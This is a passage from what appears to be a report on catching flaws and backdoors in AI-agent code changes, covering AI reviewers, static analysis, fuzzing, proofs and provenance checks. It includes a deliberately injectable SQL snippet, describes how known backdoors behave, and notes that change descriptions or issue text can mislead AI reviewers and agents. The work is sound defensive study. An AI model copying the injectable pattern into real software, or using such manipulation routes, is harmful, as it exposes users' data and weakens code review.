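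On SecPRBench, GPT-6 Sol missed 63 flaws and its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol, missed 117. If their misses were independent, about 28 flaws would have escaped both models. They both missed 59, so adding the older model to the newer one would have caught only four more flaws. The small gain may have more to do with the older model being weaker than with the models' common origin, since the other weak models also added little.

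Running the same model in two different harnesses can catch more vulnerabilities than running it in one. Of the 260 changes that the Defending Code harness finished, Opus 5.5 missed 68 in its ordinary harness, but caught 31 of those 68 in the Defending Code harness. A miss in one review therefore doesn't always mean the model lacks the knowledge to find the vulnerability, though some of the gain may be luck from having a second try.

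*When Does a Second Model Help?* (Song, 2026) tested the question more directly. It used 30 pieces of code, tutorials and presentation scripts, apparently written by Claude Opus 4.6, with 150 planted errors. Two fresh reviews by Opus together found 42.7% of the errors, while one review by Opus and one by GPT-5.4 found 56.7%. But the mixed pair was not significantly better than two reviews by GPT-5.4, so the gain may have come from using a better reviewer. The errors were also not specifically about security.

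Models can catch some of their own mistakes. In *Broken by Default*, Blain and Noiseux (2026), who founded a company that sells code analysis, asked models for a security review of 89 vulnerable code samples that the models had written. The models recognised 70 as vulnerable. But every sample was vulnerable, so a model that flagged everything would have got full marks. The samples were also short, and the test used older models.

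Self-review is already common. Selvanayagam and Ghaleb (2026), in *AI-to-AI Code Reviews of GitHub Pull Requests*, found 248,641 pull requests in which an AI product reviewed an agent's work, and in 208,145 of them the same product had written the code. The share was 95.7% for Copilot, but pull requests from Cursor and Claude Code nearly always went to another product. Two products can run on the same model, so these figures don't measure shared blind spots exactly.

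Choosing a reviewer from another developer is easy and may help a little, but telling the reviewer what the code is supposed to guarantee would probably help more. A reviewer that has only the invoice function must guess whether customers are allowed to see each other's invoices. If the project has a written rule that forbids this, the reviewer can check the code against it.

### Accidental and planted flaws

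SecPRBench's main limitation here is that it contains only accidental flaws. The flaws in Airbnb's records and MalPR-Bench also came from ordinary development or from undoing real fixes, although Chen and colleagues use the label "malicious". None of these tests shows how often an AI reviewer would find a deliberately hidden vulnerability.

AI reviewers may catch a smaller share of planted flaws than of the flaws in SecPRBench, whose programmers had no reason to mislead anyone. An attacker can choose a kind of flaw that reviewers handle badly and explain it away in the description of the change. Yang and colleagues cite two studies suggesting that persuasive descriptions can sway AI reviewers. A reviewer that reads only the repository could not have seen the altered build script in XZ, which was only in the release package.

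AI reviewers could also catch planted vulnerabilities at a higher rate than the accidental ones in SecPRBench. The benchmark includes only accidental vulnerabilities that a project's review had already missed, so they are harder to catch than average. A planted vulnerability must also give the attacker something useful, and clumsy ones stand out, as the July agent's malware did when Demir used Claude to help examine it.

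Famous attacks can't show whether AI reviewers would catch a new vulnerability, because current models have almost certainly read about the two-line Linux backdoor attempt from 2003 and the XZ backdoor. Khurana and Liman-Tinguiri propose a better test, in which a company's security engineers write deliberately insecure pull requests for its real code and never merge them. The engineers would know where each flaw was, and they would have permission, unlike the University of Minnesota researchers who submitted flawed patches to the Linux kernel.

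## Static analysis, fuzzing and comparison of behaviour

The author of a change can try to mislead an AI reviewer through the description, but most automated checks don't use it. They apply fixed rules to the code, or run the program and record what it does. Projects have long used such checks, mainly to find honest mistakes. Kokkonis and colleagues have adapted one of them to look for backdoors.

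### Static analysis

Static analysis examines a program without running it. Many tools trace data from a source, where outside input enters the program, to a sink, an operation that is dangerous if an outsider controls it. Suppose the invented online shop lets people search its orders:

```
word = request.args["search"]
query = "SELECT * FROM orders WHERE item = '" + word + "'"
database.execute(query)
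```

The first line is the source, because it takes text from the web address, and the last is the sink, because it runs a database command. The tool follows `word` into `query` and `query` into `execute`, then reports that a visitor could write part of the command. The usual fix is to pass the command and the search word to the database separately, so that the database treats the word only as data.

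CodeQL, GitHub's analysis tool, stores the whole program as a database and runs prepared queries on it to find paths like this. Such tools must be told which operations are dangerous. *CrossCommitVuln-Bench* (Majumdar, 2026) examines 15 real vulnerabilities in Python projects. In four of them, the dangerous operation was inside one of the project's own helper functions, whose name the two tools tested did not recognise.

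The invoice function in "What human reviewers catch" is a harder case because its flaw is a missing check. The invoice number travels from the web address to a database look-up, but looking something up by number is safe in itself. Majumdar found no rule in either tool that reports a missing check. In one project, more than 200 web addresses lacked a permission check, and the only relevant alert was a low-severity one about a hard-coded key.

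A project can write a rule for its static analysis tool, such as requiring every function that handles a web request to call the permission check. A language model might notice a missing check without such a rule. Peter Stöckli, a security researcher at GitHub, says in Help Net Security's *Too many instructions can hold back AI security audits* (2026) that models are good at finding inconsistencies, such as one address without a check that similar addresses have. However, Codex struggled with this kind of comparison in the tests by Chen and colleagues.

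### How many real vulnerabilities static tools find

In the largest recent measurement, *Fixed Detectors, Moving Code*, Tang, Zhang and Cai (2026) collected 10,000 vulnerable and 10,000 fixed versions of code from 1,116 C and C++ projects. They ran three well-known tools on this code, including three releases each of CodeQL and Infer.

| Tool and release year | Vulnerable versions flagged | Fixed versions flagged |
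|---|---|---|
| CodeQL, 2021 | 7.1% | 7.5% |
| CodeQL, 2024 | 13.1% | 13.0% |
| CodeQL, 2026 | 20.7% | 21.3% |
| Infer, 2021 | 3.6% | 3.7% |
| Infer, 2024 | 10.2% | 5.1% |
| Infer, 2026 | 8.5% | 8.9% |
| Semgrep | 46.5% | 47.9% |

Only the 2024 release of Infer flagged vulnerable code noticeably more often than fixed code. CodeQL flags nearly three times as many vulnerable versions as it did in 2021, but the number of fixed versions it flags has grown just as fast.

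Even the first column overstates the tools' performance, because Tang and colleagues counted a version as flagged if the tool gave at least one relevant warning in a file that the security fix changed, whatever the warning was about. In HAProxy, a program that distributes web traffic, the 2024 release of CodeQL warned about a possible overflow on the same line in both the vulnerable and the fixed version. The fix dealt with an empty header and did not change that line. The study counted this as one correct detection and one false alarm, although CodeQL had not found the vulnerability.

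The second column may make the tools look slightly worse than they are, because a warning on fixed code can point to a different real flaw. Still, a warning from these tools gives almost no information about whether a changed file contains the known vulnerability.

A clean result is not very informative. Semgrep failed to parse some code or ran out of time in 79% of the runs, according to the logs, yet every run reported success. A maintainer who sees only a green tick would not know that the tool had skipped something.

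Smaller studies also find that these tools miss many vulnerabilities. *QLCoder* (2025) reports that CodeQL's standard queries found 20% of 130 known vulnerabilities. In the paper's own system, a language model writes a new query for each known vulnerability, and it succeeded for 53.4% of them. Such queries could help a project find further copies of a flaw once someone has discovered the first.

*Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation* (2026) reports that human reviewers judged 39% of samples of AI-written code vulnerable. Semgrep flagged a similar share, 40%, but agreed with the reviewers on only 65% of the samples. CodeQL flagged 20% and agreed on 61%, the same rate that a tool would achieve by calling every sample secure.

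Scanning only the latest change can miss vulnerabilities that a scan of the whole program would catch. Majumdar chose 15 vulnerabilities that had each built up over at least two harmless-looking commits, with a median of 58 days between the first and last. Semgrep and Bandit, a tool for Python, gave a relevant warning on one of the commits for two of the vulnerabilities. When they scanned the whole program just before the fix, they caught four. The sample is small and deliberately difficult, but it supports what practitioners said in 2024 about commits that are dangerous only in combination.

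Static analysis is still useful. *Finding 709 Defects in 258 Projects* (2023) found hundreds of defects by running CodeQL on open-source software for embedded devices. But *Many Tools, Few Exploitable Vulnerabilities* (2026), a survey of 246 analysis tools, found that most concentrate on a few well-known problems, mainly injection and memory errors. The tools can catch some of these problems in agents' changes with little effort, but they are not a reliable way to decide that a change is safe.

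### Fuzzing in the build pipeline

Fuzzing runs the program and watches for failures. A modern fuzzer starts with a few ordinary inputs, such as valid image files, and alters them slightly. It keeps any altered input that reaches code no earlier input had reached, then alters that one too, so it gradually reaches deeper into the program. A small piece of code called a fuzzing harness passes the inputs to the project, and the fuzzer can test only the parts of the project that the harness uses.

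Many memory errors do not crash a program by themselves, so developers usually fuzz a version compiled with sanitizers, which are checks that stop the program as soon as it does something like read past the end of a buffer. This works well for memory errors. By August 2023, according to Kokkonis and colleagues, Google's OSS-Fuzz service had helped fix more than 10,000 vulnerabilities in 1,000 projects. CIFuzz, its companion for build pipelines, compiles each commit and fuzzes it briefly.

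*NIFuzz* (2025) explains that a fuzzer can usually distinguish only between a successful run and a crash. If a fuzzer requested a million invoice numbers from the shop, it would get a PDF for some and "not found" for the rest. Both are normal replies, so the fuzzer would not detect that invoice 1042 belongs to another customer.

Researchers have done little to fill this gap. *Adaptive and AI-Augmented Security Testing* (2026) surveyed methods that adjust their tests based on earlier results. Of the 12 systems with substantial feedback of this kind, only two checked specifically for security violations. The others relied on general signs such as crashes, newly reached code or whether the program compiled, none of which shows that someone has bypassed a login.

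### How Lily compares two versions

Kokkonis and colleagues' tool, Lily, uses the same short fuzzing runs but looks for unusual behaviour instead of crashes. It does this by monitoring system calls, the requests a program must make to the operating system to open a file, use the network or start another program. For each input, Lily records which types of system call the program makes, but not their order or number. Kokkonis and colleagues argue that a useful backdoor in an ordinary program has to make such calls, because it must affect something outside the program.

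When somebody proposes a commit or release, Lily goes through five steps:

1. It runs the new version on inputs saved while fuzzing earlier versions, and records every set of system calls that appears. These sets define normal behaviour.
2. It fuzzes the new version to find inputs that reach new code.
3. It compares the system calls for each input that the fuzzer keeps with the normal sets. If they match one of the sets, Lily treats the input as safe.
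4. If they match none, it runs the same input on the old version. If the old version makes the same calls, the change did not cause the odd behaviour, and Lily again treats the input as safe. Otherwise it raises an alert.
5. It finds the changed lines that ran for the suspicious input and the lines that led to the unusual calls. It reports where they overlap, along with the input itself.

Lily defines normal behaviour by running the version under suspicion, which helps it avoid flagging harmless changes. For example, if an honest update makes a server write every login to a file, each login makes an extra system call that would look new in comparison with the old version. Because the call also happens on ordinary logins, Lily records it as normal. Step 4 deals with rare but legitimate operations that the old version could also perform but that earlier fuzzing had not reached.

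Kokkonis and colleagues measured what each condition contributes by switching the other one off.

| Lily raises an alert if the behaviour is | Runs on safe commits with a false alarm | Runs on safe releases with a false alarm |
|---|---|---|
| Unusual for the new version | 14% | 20% |
| Absent from the old version | 10% | 58% |
| Both | 0.2% | 4.3% |

Looking only for new behaviour works particularly badly for releases, since the purpose of a release is often to add some.

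While testing the doctored release of vsFTPd, for example, the fuzzer eventually generated a user name containing a smiley and kept it because that input ran code no earlier input had reached. The program responded by opening a network port, waiting for a connection and providing a command line. No saved input had produced that combination of system calls, and the previous release did not produce it for the same user name. The two releases differed by 1,407 lines in five files, but Lily's report pointed to seven lines in one file, which are enough for a programmer to see that the server gives a stranger control.

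### How well Lily worked

Kokkonis and colleagues tested Lily on 13 open-source programs, including the database SQLite and the image library libpng. They used 432 safe commits and 13 with a backdoor, plus 50 safe releases and 50 with a backdoor. Three of the 13 backdoors came from real attacks on vsFTPd, ProFTPD and PHP, and researchers wrote the other ten. Fuzzing results vary by chance, so the team ran every test 20 times, for ten minutes each time.

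| | Runs that detected the backdoor | Runs on safe changes with a false alarm |
|---|---|---|
| Commits | 90% | 0.2% |
| Releases | 83% | 4.3% |

Lily detected every backdoor in at least one run. The misses were partly due to chance in which inputs the fuzzer tried, so running Lily again should help. Based on the detection rate for each program, two runs would miss about 2.5% of the backdoored commits, compared with 10% for one run. The AI reviewers in the previous section, by contrast, tended to miss the same flaws.

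False alarms were less random and came mostly from a few updates. Two safe updates to libsndfile, a sound library, set off an alert in every run and produced 40 of the 43 false alarms for releases. Four large merges in PHP produced 12 of the 17 false alarms for commits. A project might therefore see no false alarms for months, then have one harmless release fail every time it repeats the test. In the release tests, reports averaged between one and 12 lines per program, even when the diff ran to two million lines.

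The detection rates apply only to code that the fuzzer can reach. On 337 commits that changed code, ten minutes of fuzzing covered only about 32% of the affected code on average, mainly because many projects' harnesses were incomplete or old. Kokkonis and colleagues report nearly complete coverage for most commits tested with modern harnesses, and expect coverage to improve as projects maintain theirs.

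The claim that Lily would have prevented the three real attacks is also a little strong. Lily detected the ProFTPD backdoor in only 34 of 80 release runs, and the real ProFTPD attackers used a release package. The test did not include the XZ backdoor, the best hidden of the real ones. The team that built Lily also created the collection of backdoors used to test it, and nobody has yet reported a trial on a live project.

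In one experiment, deliberate attempts to evade Lily cut its detection rates to roughly half. A stricter mode restored the rates but raised false alarms to 2.5% of runs for commits and 18% for releases.

### Why most alerts would be false

Even with a false-alarm rate of 0.2%, most of Lily's alerts would be false if malicious commits are very rare, as they probably are. If one commit in 100,000 is malicious, Lily would raise an average of 0.9 correct alerts (90% of one) and about 200 false ones (0.2% of 99,999) per 100,000 commits. About one alert in 220 would then be real.

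In general, if *p* is the share of commits that are malicious, *d* the detection rate and *f* the false-alarm rate, then

share of alerts that are real = *pd* / (*pd* + (1 − *p*)*f*)

Nobody knows *p*, and the answer depends heavily on it.

| Malicious commits | Correct alerts per 100,000 commits | False alerts per 100,000 commits | Alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 1,000 | 90 | 200 | About 1 in 3 |
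| 1 in 10,000 | 9 | 200 | About 1 in 23 |
| 1 in 100,000 | 0.9 | 200 | About 1 in 220 |
| 1 in 1,000,000 | 0.09 | 200 | About 1 in 2,200 |

If Lily caught every backdoor, the share of alerts that are real would rise only from one in 220 to about one in 200. Reducing false alarms tenfold would raise it to one in 23. For releases, if one in 100,000 were malicious, 83% detection and a 4.3% false alarm rate would mean that only about one alert in 5,200 was real.

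Checking the alerts is still manageable for commits. A project that merges 20 commits a day would get a false alarm about every 25 days. If each takes ten minutes to check, because the report identifies the lines involved, maintainers across many projects would spend about 37 hours for every backdoor they found. That seems like little work to stop something like the XZ attack. The bigger risk is that a maintainer whose last 50 alerts were all false will dismiss the next one without reading it.

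How much an alert should change a maintainer's mind depends on how much more often the tool flags bad code than safe code. Lily flags 90% of backdoored commits and 0.2% of safe ones, so an alert multiplies the odds that a commit is malicious by 450. The 2026 release of CodeQL flagged vulnerable versions slightly less often than fixed ones, so in that test an alert was not evidence of a vulnerability. AI reviewers find far more vulnerabilities, but they also report problems in so much repaired code that a project could not sensibly block every change they flag. Their findings are more useful as points for a person to check.

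The calculation assumes that every commit is equally likely to be malicious. A project could use other evidence, such as an unfamiliar account or an unusual route into the repository, to decide which alerts to spend more time on. The section "Provenance, identity and permissions" covers detection from commit records.

### Flaws that only remove a safeguard

Lily works because the backdoors in its test add behaviour, but a planted vulnerability may add none. When a customer of the invented shop downloads somebody else's invoice, the program reads a record, opens a file and sends it, as it does when customers download their own. The system calls are the same, so Lily would not flag the download.

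The typo that disabled Landlock in XZ would be hard to detect for another reason. Lily learns what is normal from the new version of a program, so that legitimate updates don't cause false alarms. If a change stops the program from ever switching on a protection, the system calls for that protection are missing from every run, and Lily would probably record the unprotected program as normal.

Some backdoors also produce too little observable behaviour to detect. The two lines in the 2003 attempt to backdoor the kernel only changed a number in memory while the kernel was answering a system call that the program was allowed to make. However, Lily was not designed to examine kernels in any case.

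A tool can detect a missing safeguard only if it has a description of what the safeguard was supposed to guarantee. People can write this description as a test or as a statement to prove.

### Tests of security properties

An ordinary test checks one example, such as a customer downloading her own invoice. A property test states a rule and tries to break it with many generated examples. For the invoice function, it could look like this:

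```
@given(integers(1, 5000))
def test_invoices_stay_private(number):
    reply = log_in("alice").get(f"/invoices/{number}")
    if reply.status_code == 200:
        assert owner_of(number) == "alice"
```

The first line makes the testing tool try whole numbers from 1 to 5,000. Each time, the test logs in as Alice and requests the invoice with that number. If the request succeeds (code 200), the invoice must be hers. If the permission check is missing, whether because an agent forgot it or an attacker left it out, the test fails as soon as it reaches an existing invoice that belongs to someone else.

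If `Invoice.find` already restricts the search to Alice's invoices, the test passes, and nobody has to open another file to find out.

*Anota* (2025) proposes that developers annotate their code with the rules it must follow, so that a fuzzer can report a violation much as a sanitizer reports a memory error. *NIFuzz* uses fuzzing to look for leaks of secret information. A common way to test for such a leak is to run a program twice with the same public input but different secrets. If an outsider can see a difference in the output, some of the secret has leaked.

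The main weakness of these tests is that they check only the rules someone thought to write. A test for invoices won't catch a flaw in a new page that shows delivery addresses. Generated examples can also miss a check that fails only in a rare situation. An agent that changes the code may also change the tests in the same pull request, so a project should require a named person to approve any edit to its security tests, as some projects do for workflow files.

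Agents could make such tests much easier to write. In *Generating Proof-of-Vulnerability Tests to Help Enhance the Security of Complex Software*, Kanchi, Zang and colleagues (2026) used Codex to write tests meant to show that an application is exposed to a known flaw in a library it uses. Of the 152 tests Codex wrote for 33 pairs of Java applications and libraries, 141 compiled and 84 (55%) demonstrated a working attack.

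That success rate is useful for a tedious job, but Codex was given a description of the flaw and an example test from the library. Kanchi and colleagues also used a second model to judge whether each test had worked, and it was right about only 103 of them, so a person still has to check. The experiment did not cover the harder task of working out which rule a new feature ought to obey when there is no known flaw to copy.

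### Formal proof

A formal proof covers every possible input, including those that tests never try. Suppose a program has a list of ten items, numbered 0 to 9, and reads the item at position `i`. An analysis tool may be able to prove from the surrounding code that `i` is always between 0 and 9. In that case, the program cannot read past the end of the list, whatever an attacker sends.

Abstract interpretation is a method of static analysis that works with ranges and other summaries instead of actual values. *Finding 709 Defects in 258 Projects* names IKOS as an open-source tool that uses this method and guarantees soundness. A sound tool catches every error of the kinds it covers, provided that its assumptions hold. It also raises false alarms, because it must report any code it cannot prove safe.

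A project can rely on proofs despite the halting problem, because it can refuse any change to a critical part unless the proof succeeds. Programmers then have to write that part simply enough for the proof tool to handle.

Formal verification helps against planted vulnerabilities because removing a safeguard breaks the proof that depends on it. If a project has proved that its shop software never sends an invoice to anyone but the invoice's owner, a change that drops the ownership check will fail verification, however innocent it looks. To get the change accepted, an attacker would have to weaken the statement being proved, which is usually much shorter than the code and easier for a person to review.

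A formal proof covers only the properties someone has specified. A program proven never to misuse memory can still send a customer's invoices to the wrong person. Even a proof that invoices go only to their owners assumes that the database records the right owner and that the build tools work correctly. Writing and maintaining proofs takes skilled work, so they make most sense for small parts of the code that rarely change, such as the function that decides who may see which data.

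### Scanning an agent's fix again

Agents also write fixes for the flaws that static analysis finds. GitHub began a public preview of Agentic Autofix in July 2026. According to GitHub's *Agentic autofix for code scanning alerts in public preview* (2026), a maintainer assigns an alert to Copilot, which explores the relevant files, writes a fix and runs CodeQL again. If the alert is still there, Copilot can revise the fix. It then opens a draft pull request, usually within two to four minutes, for a person to review.

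Rerunning the analysis catches fixes that don't work by CodeQL's own standard. The announcement describes this as rerunning the original analysis, but GitHub's *About autofix for code scanning* states that Copilot uses only CodeQL's standard set of queries. Copilot therefore cannot confirm a fix for an alert that came from the extended security set or a project's own queries. GitHub also does not guarantee the quality of fixes for alerts from other companies' tools.

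Rescanning the code with CodeQL after a fix can miss the same kinds of flaws as the first scan. If a fix removes the dangerous database command but also drops a permission check, the original alert disappears, and CodeQL may have no query for the new flaw. In Help Net Security's *GitHub Agentic Autofix and the question of who owns a bad AI patch* (2026), Marcelo Oliveira, a vice-president at GitHub, says the agent also runs the project's own tests. Those tests would catch the dropped check if they included a property test for it.

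Oliveira says that if a fix closes one vulnerability and opens another, GitHub is accountable for the quality of its suggestion and customers decide what to merge. This leaves the final check to reviewers who already have too much to read. He says an earlier version of Autofix helped customers clear old security alerts four times as fast as people working alone. That is the company's own figure, and it measures how quickly alerts close. Oliveira would rather measure whether fewer vulnerabilities reach users, and he advises customers to set the pace of fixes so that a backlog of alerts doesn't become a pile of unreviewed pull requests.

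Attackers can also mislead an agent that writes fixes, as they can any other agent. GitHub notes that Copilot follows a repository's custom instructions when it writes a fix, so those instructions need the same protection as AGENTS.md. If an attacker misled the agent into adding a vulnerability, a repeat scan would catch it only if it matched one of CodeQL's queries.

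## Provenance, identity and permissions

Projects record who submitted a change, who approved it and which machine built the release. They use these records to determine who wrote the code and whether the package that users download contains the tested code. A property test that shows customers see only their own invoices can't establish either of these things about the invoice function.

### Signed commits

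Git calculates each commit's identifier from the files, the author's name, the date, the message and the previous commit's identifier. Altering any of these changes the identifiers of that commit and all later ones. A developer can also sign a commit with a private key. Anyone with the matching public key can then confirm that the holder of the private key signed exactly that commit.

In 2021, intruders broke into PHP's server and committed code under the names of known developers. Commit signatures would have helped, because the intruders could not have produced those developers' signatures without their keys. The signature check would have had to run outside the breached server, where the intruders could not disable it.

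A valid signature doesn't show what the signer intended, as the XZ releases demonstrated, or even who wrote the code. A coding agent that works on a developer's machine and can use the developer's key may sign its commits with that same key. Giving the agent its own key would at least distinguish its work from the developer's, but it wouldn't show who told the agent what to write.

The person behind a key may not exist either. GitHub investigated a North Korean team that had invented at least 135 people, with generated portraits and fake passports. Biometric Update's *Github reveals how North Korean hackers create synthetic identities to infiltrate businesses* reports that the team passed just over 40% of the identity checks it attempted on email and professional networking sites. The team used its invented identities to gain access to at least 48 private code bases.

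### The SLSA levels

Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts (SLSA) is an industry standard for grading how well projects protect their code and releases from tampering. Version 1.2 kept the existing Build Track and added a Source Track, which covers how people write, review and manage code (SLSA, 2025).

Both tracks rely on attestations, which are statements about how a change or a file came to exist. The system that handled the change or built the file normally issues the attestation, and a signature protects it against forgery.

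| Level | What it requires | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Source 1 | A version control system | Someone rewrites the history |
| Source 2 | A permanent history, with records of who changed what | One person or stolen account adds a bad change |
| Source 3 | Automatic enforcement of the project's own rules | A bad change satisfies the rules |
| Source 4 | Agreement of two trusted people on every change | Both people miss the flaw |
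| Build 1 | A record of how the package was built | Someone forges the record |
| Build 2 | A record signed by a hosted build service | Someone tampers with the build while it runs |
| Build 3 | A build service hardened against tampering | The source code already contains the flaw |

SLSA's *Source* says that a project that adopts a source level makes no claim about earlier versions of its code. Reaching Source 4 would therefore not remove a vulnerability that somebody planted a year earlier.

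The standard also requires projects to prevent anyone from moving a release label to different code. The attacker moved labels this way to spread malicious code through changed-files in March 2025. The standard exempts labels that a project moves on purpose, such as "latest". Many component owners treat a label like `@v5` that way, so users still need to pin exact versions.

### A second person's approval

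At SushiSwap, a cryptocurrency exchange, a contractor with access to the repository pushed a malicious commit that redirected funds to the contractor. The contractor could change the code alone, so there was no need to trick anyone into approving it. SLSA lists this as an attack that a second reviewer could have caught.

Source 4 counts only humans as trusted persons. It requires either that the submitter and the reviewer both be trusted, or that two trusted people review the change. If an agent submits a change from its own account, two people must therefore approve it. If a developer submits the agent's work, approval from one other person is enough. Agarwal and colleagues found that the only reviewer is often the person who started the agent, so many projects don't meet this requirement.

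An organisation may exempt a "trusted robot" from the rule. The standard's examples include Dependabot, which proposes updates to a project's dependencies. To qualify, a robot must have an identity and code that no one person can influence alone. A coding agent could meet that condition and still be unsafe to exempt, because a stranger can redirect it with text in an issue without changing its code.

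SLSA is stricter in the threat list that accompanies the standard, where it recommends that two people review every change, including those written by robots. It also warns that someone who controls both a robot account and a personal account can get around this review, for example by influencing a robot that has permission to contribute or approve code.

Approval also has to cover the final version of a change. In July 2026, the agent that attacked myNetwork rewrote its branch during the discussion. If a project lets an earlier approval stand after such an edit, it can merge code that nobody has read.

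Provenance, identity and permission controls don't help reviewers notice a hidden vulnerability. SLSA's *Source integrity threats* treats malicious changes that look benign as outside the standard's scope, along with reviewers who approve without reading and trusted people who collude. Two approvals are meant to show that a change matches the project's intent, but if the change contains a planted vulnerability, they may show only that two people believed its description.

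### What a build attestation proves

Suppose a new version of the image library comes with an attestation, a signed statement from the build service that it built this exact file from a particular commit in the official repository. Before installing the library, a program can check the signature, the repository and the file's fingerprint, and reject the file if any of them is wrong.

Attestation checks help protect against stolen credentials. Attackers once used leaked credentials to replace a file that users downloaded from Codecov, a service that measures how much of a program its tests cover. An attestation check would have shown that the file did not come from the expected build. The backdoored LiteLLM packages, which attackers published directly to PyPI, would probably have failed such a check too. But the user's software has to require an attestation, or an attacker can leave it out.

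At the lowest build level, the provenance record may be unsigned and is easy to forge. At Build 2, the hosted build service signs it. According to SLSA's *Build*, Build 3 also prevents one build from influencing another and keeps the signing key out of reach of the project's own build steps. If those steps could reach the key, a malicious script in the pipeline could steal it and sign anything.

A malicious release can have an accurate attestation. An attacker added a password-stealing script to one project's official repository, and in November 2026 the project's automated publishing included it in a PHP package. An attestation would have correctly identified the official repository as the package's source. SLSA does not cover code quality or producers who intend harm.

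A package's SLSA level doesn't cover its dependencies. According to SLSA, applying the standard to every dependency would have stopped the event-stream attack, because the malicious package did not match its public source. The attacker could have responded by committing the malicious code to the dependency's repository, which would have been riskier only if someone was reading the source of a little-known package.

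### Reproducible builds

An attestation is only as reliable as the machine that issues it. The SolarWinds attackers controlled the build server, so the company unknowingly signed a program they had altered. With reproducible builds, users don't have to trust a single machine, because independent parties can compile the same source with the same tools and compare hashes of the results.

Build tools often put the time or a folder name into their output, and one different byte changes the fingerprint. A project has to remove such differences before a mismatch between two builds can indicate tampering. If SolarWinds had done so, a second build of Orion on a clean machine would have exposed the swapped file.

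Matching fingerprints show that the program corresponds to its source. If the source lacks a permission check, everyone who builds it gets the same vulnerable program. Their results will also match if they all use a compiler doctored in the way Ken Thompson described.

The files a build starts from also matter. Linux distributions built XZ from its release download, which contained the altered script. Two parties who repeated a distribution's build from that download would have produced the same backdoor and matching fingerprints. They would have discovered the problem only by comparing the download with the repository, or by comparing programs built from each.

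### Looking for unusual commits

Commit records can also serve as evidence about whether a change is suspicious. Gonzalez, Zimmermann and colleagues (2021), in *Anomalicious*, built a tool that ignores the code and looks only at these records. It has seven rules, and a commit breaks one if:

- it changes sensitive files, such as build settings
- the author has never touched many of its files before
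- the author isn't a main contributor to most of its files
- it adds an unusual number of files and touches none that the author mainly looks after
- several of its measurements, such as lines added or files deleted, are far from the average for the author or project
- the author is untrusted
- it belongs to a rejected pull request

The tool uses seven further rules to decide whether to trust an author. They penalise, for example, a new account, few commits, or a commit history made mostly on one day. The tool flags a commit that breaks a large enough share of the main rules, and its report lists the rules broken.

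Gonzalez and colleagues first ran it on 100 JavaScript projects with no known malicious commits. It flagged less than 1% of commits in 56 of the projects and less than 5% in 99. In Angular.js, a popular framework for building websites, it flagged 34 of 8,978 commits. Most of these changed dependencies or development tools, which honest maintainers sometimes need to do.

The second experiment used 15 repositories that each contained a known malicious commit. The tool found eight of these commits (53%), including the one in event-stream. Thirteen of the 15 repositories had the same malware, so this was a narrow test. By the paper's counts, the tool flagged 114 of about 2,350 commits, so roughly one alert in 14 pointed to a known malicious commit. A few of the other 106 flagged commits showed odd behaviour that the team could not explain, so not all of those alerts were mistakes.

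The low alert rates and the 53% come from different settings. The tool flagged commits that broke at least half the rules in the first experiment, and at least a third in the second. The event-stream commit broke exactly a third, so the first setting would have missed it. The team chose the one-third threshold after trying several on the same 15 repositories, which tends to make a result look better than it is.

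With the looser setting, a flag from Anomalicious multiplies the odds that a commit is malicious by about 12, compared with 450 for an alert from Lily. If one commit in 100,000 were malicious, only about one flag in 8,500 would be correct. Anomalicious is therefore better suited to choosing commits for closer review than to blocking them.

The detector missed seven malicious commits, all from authors it had classed as trusted. An agent that works through an established developer's account would benefit from the same trust. An agent with its own account could look suspicious even when its work is harmless, because it may make many commits in a day and edit files it has never touched.

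### PolinRider

The PolinRider campaign, which researchers link to North Korea, tampers with commit records. It often begins with a fake job interview in which a developer runs an infected coding test. The malware then uses the developer's GitHub access. According to ThreatRoundup's *PolinRider Has Poisoned 7,600 GitHub Repos, and Ethereum Steers It* (2026), the malware rewrites the developer's existing commits to add malicious code, keeping the original author, message and date. It publishes the result with a force-push, which replaces a branch's history instead of adding to it.

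Someone who glances at the list of commits sees nothing new. The malware steals passwords, browser data and cryptocurrency wallets from people who run the code.

Researchers kept finding more infected repositories during 2026. OpenSourceMalware's *PolinRider Rides Again* counted 675 in early March and 1,951 about five weeks later. By late November, the security company Apiiro had found at least 7,609, belonging to 2,330 accounts. The attackers had hit 2,040 of these between 27 October and 6 November. The Hacker News (2026) reports signs that the campaign began as early as February 2025.

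Anomalicious would probably be poor at detecting PolinRider's altered commits. The apparent author is often the repository's owner, who has a long record, and the commit has an old date. By default, the tool counts `.json` and `.xml` files as sensitive but not the `.js` and `.py` files where PolinRider often puts its code. The tool also reads the repository's current history, so it would examine the altered commit with no indication that this commit had replaced another.

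A rewritten commit has a new identifier, even if everything a person normally reads is the same. To detect this, Smith's *Malware Modified Your Git Commits* advises comparing identifiers with those in another developer's clean copy, signed release tags or build records. GitHub keeps a separate log of pushes, and Clubic's *108 malwares dévoilés* says only this log shows the real changes.

Rewriting a commit also invalidates its original signature. But if the developer's key is on the infected machine, the malware may be able to sign the new version. A key that requires the developer to press a button for each signature would be harder to abuse.

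An alarm for every rewritten history would often be set off by harmless changes, because developers often tidy up their commits. *Altered Histories in Version Control System Repositories* (2025) examined 111 million public repositories and found rewritten history in 1.22 million, or about 1.1%. Git's documentation explains how to rewrite commits, but advises developers to treat work as final once they have shared it.

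A project can enforce that advice on its main branch. Source 2 requires a ban on force-pushes, and GitHub blocks them by default on branches that a project has protected. Either would stop this method, as long as the rule also applies to administrators and the malware can't use the developer's permissions to turn it off.

The attacker could still add an ordinary commit, but it would appear at the top of the history with a new identifier, and a project that required a second approval could reject it. Most of PolinRider's victims are individual developers, who may have nobody else to approve their changes.

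### Rules for AI contributions

A project can also ask contributors to say when they used AI. The Linux kernel project asks for an "Assisted-by:" line in the commit message, naming the tool and model. In the Linux Foundation survey that Help Net Security describes, about a third of projects had a formal policy allowing AI-assisted contributions, and one in ten banned them. The rest had no written policy or were still working on one. The policies mostly require contributors to disclose AI use and to take responsibility for reviewing their own work.

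GitHub offers a cruder control. A project can temporarily limit pull requests to accounts more than a day old, to previous contributors or to collaborators. It can also limit pull requests to collaborators indefinitely or turn them off. These restrictions reduce the number of submissions but shut out honest newcomers.

None of these rules is enough to decide whether to trust a change. The XZ attacker could have followed every rule of this kind. A malicious contributor can leave out the "Assisted-by:" line, and many honest ones already do. A limit on new contributors doesn't stop someone who has stolen an established contributor's account. Kai Gritun, the agent that had several changes merged within two weeks, would then have counted as an earlier contributor to those projects.

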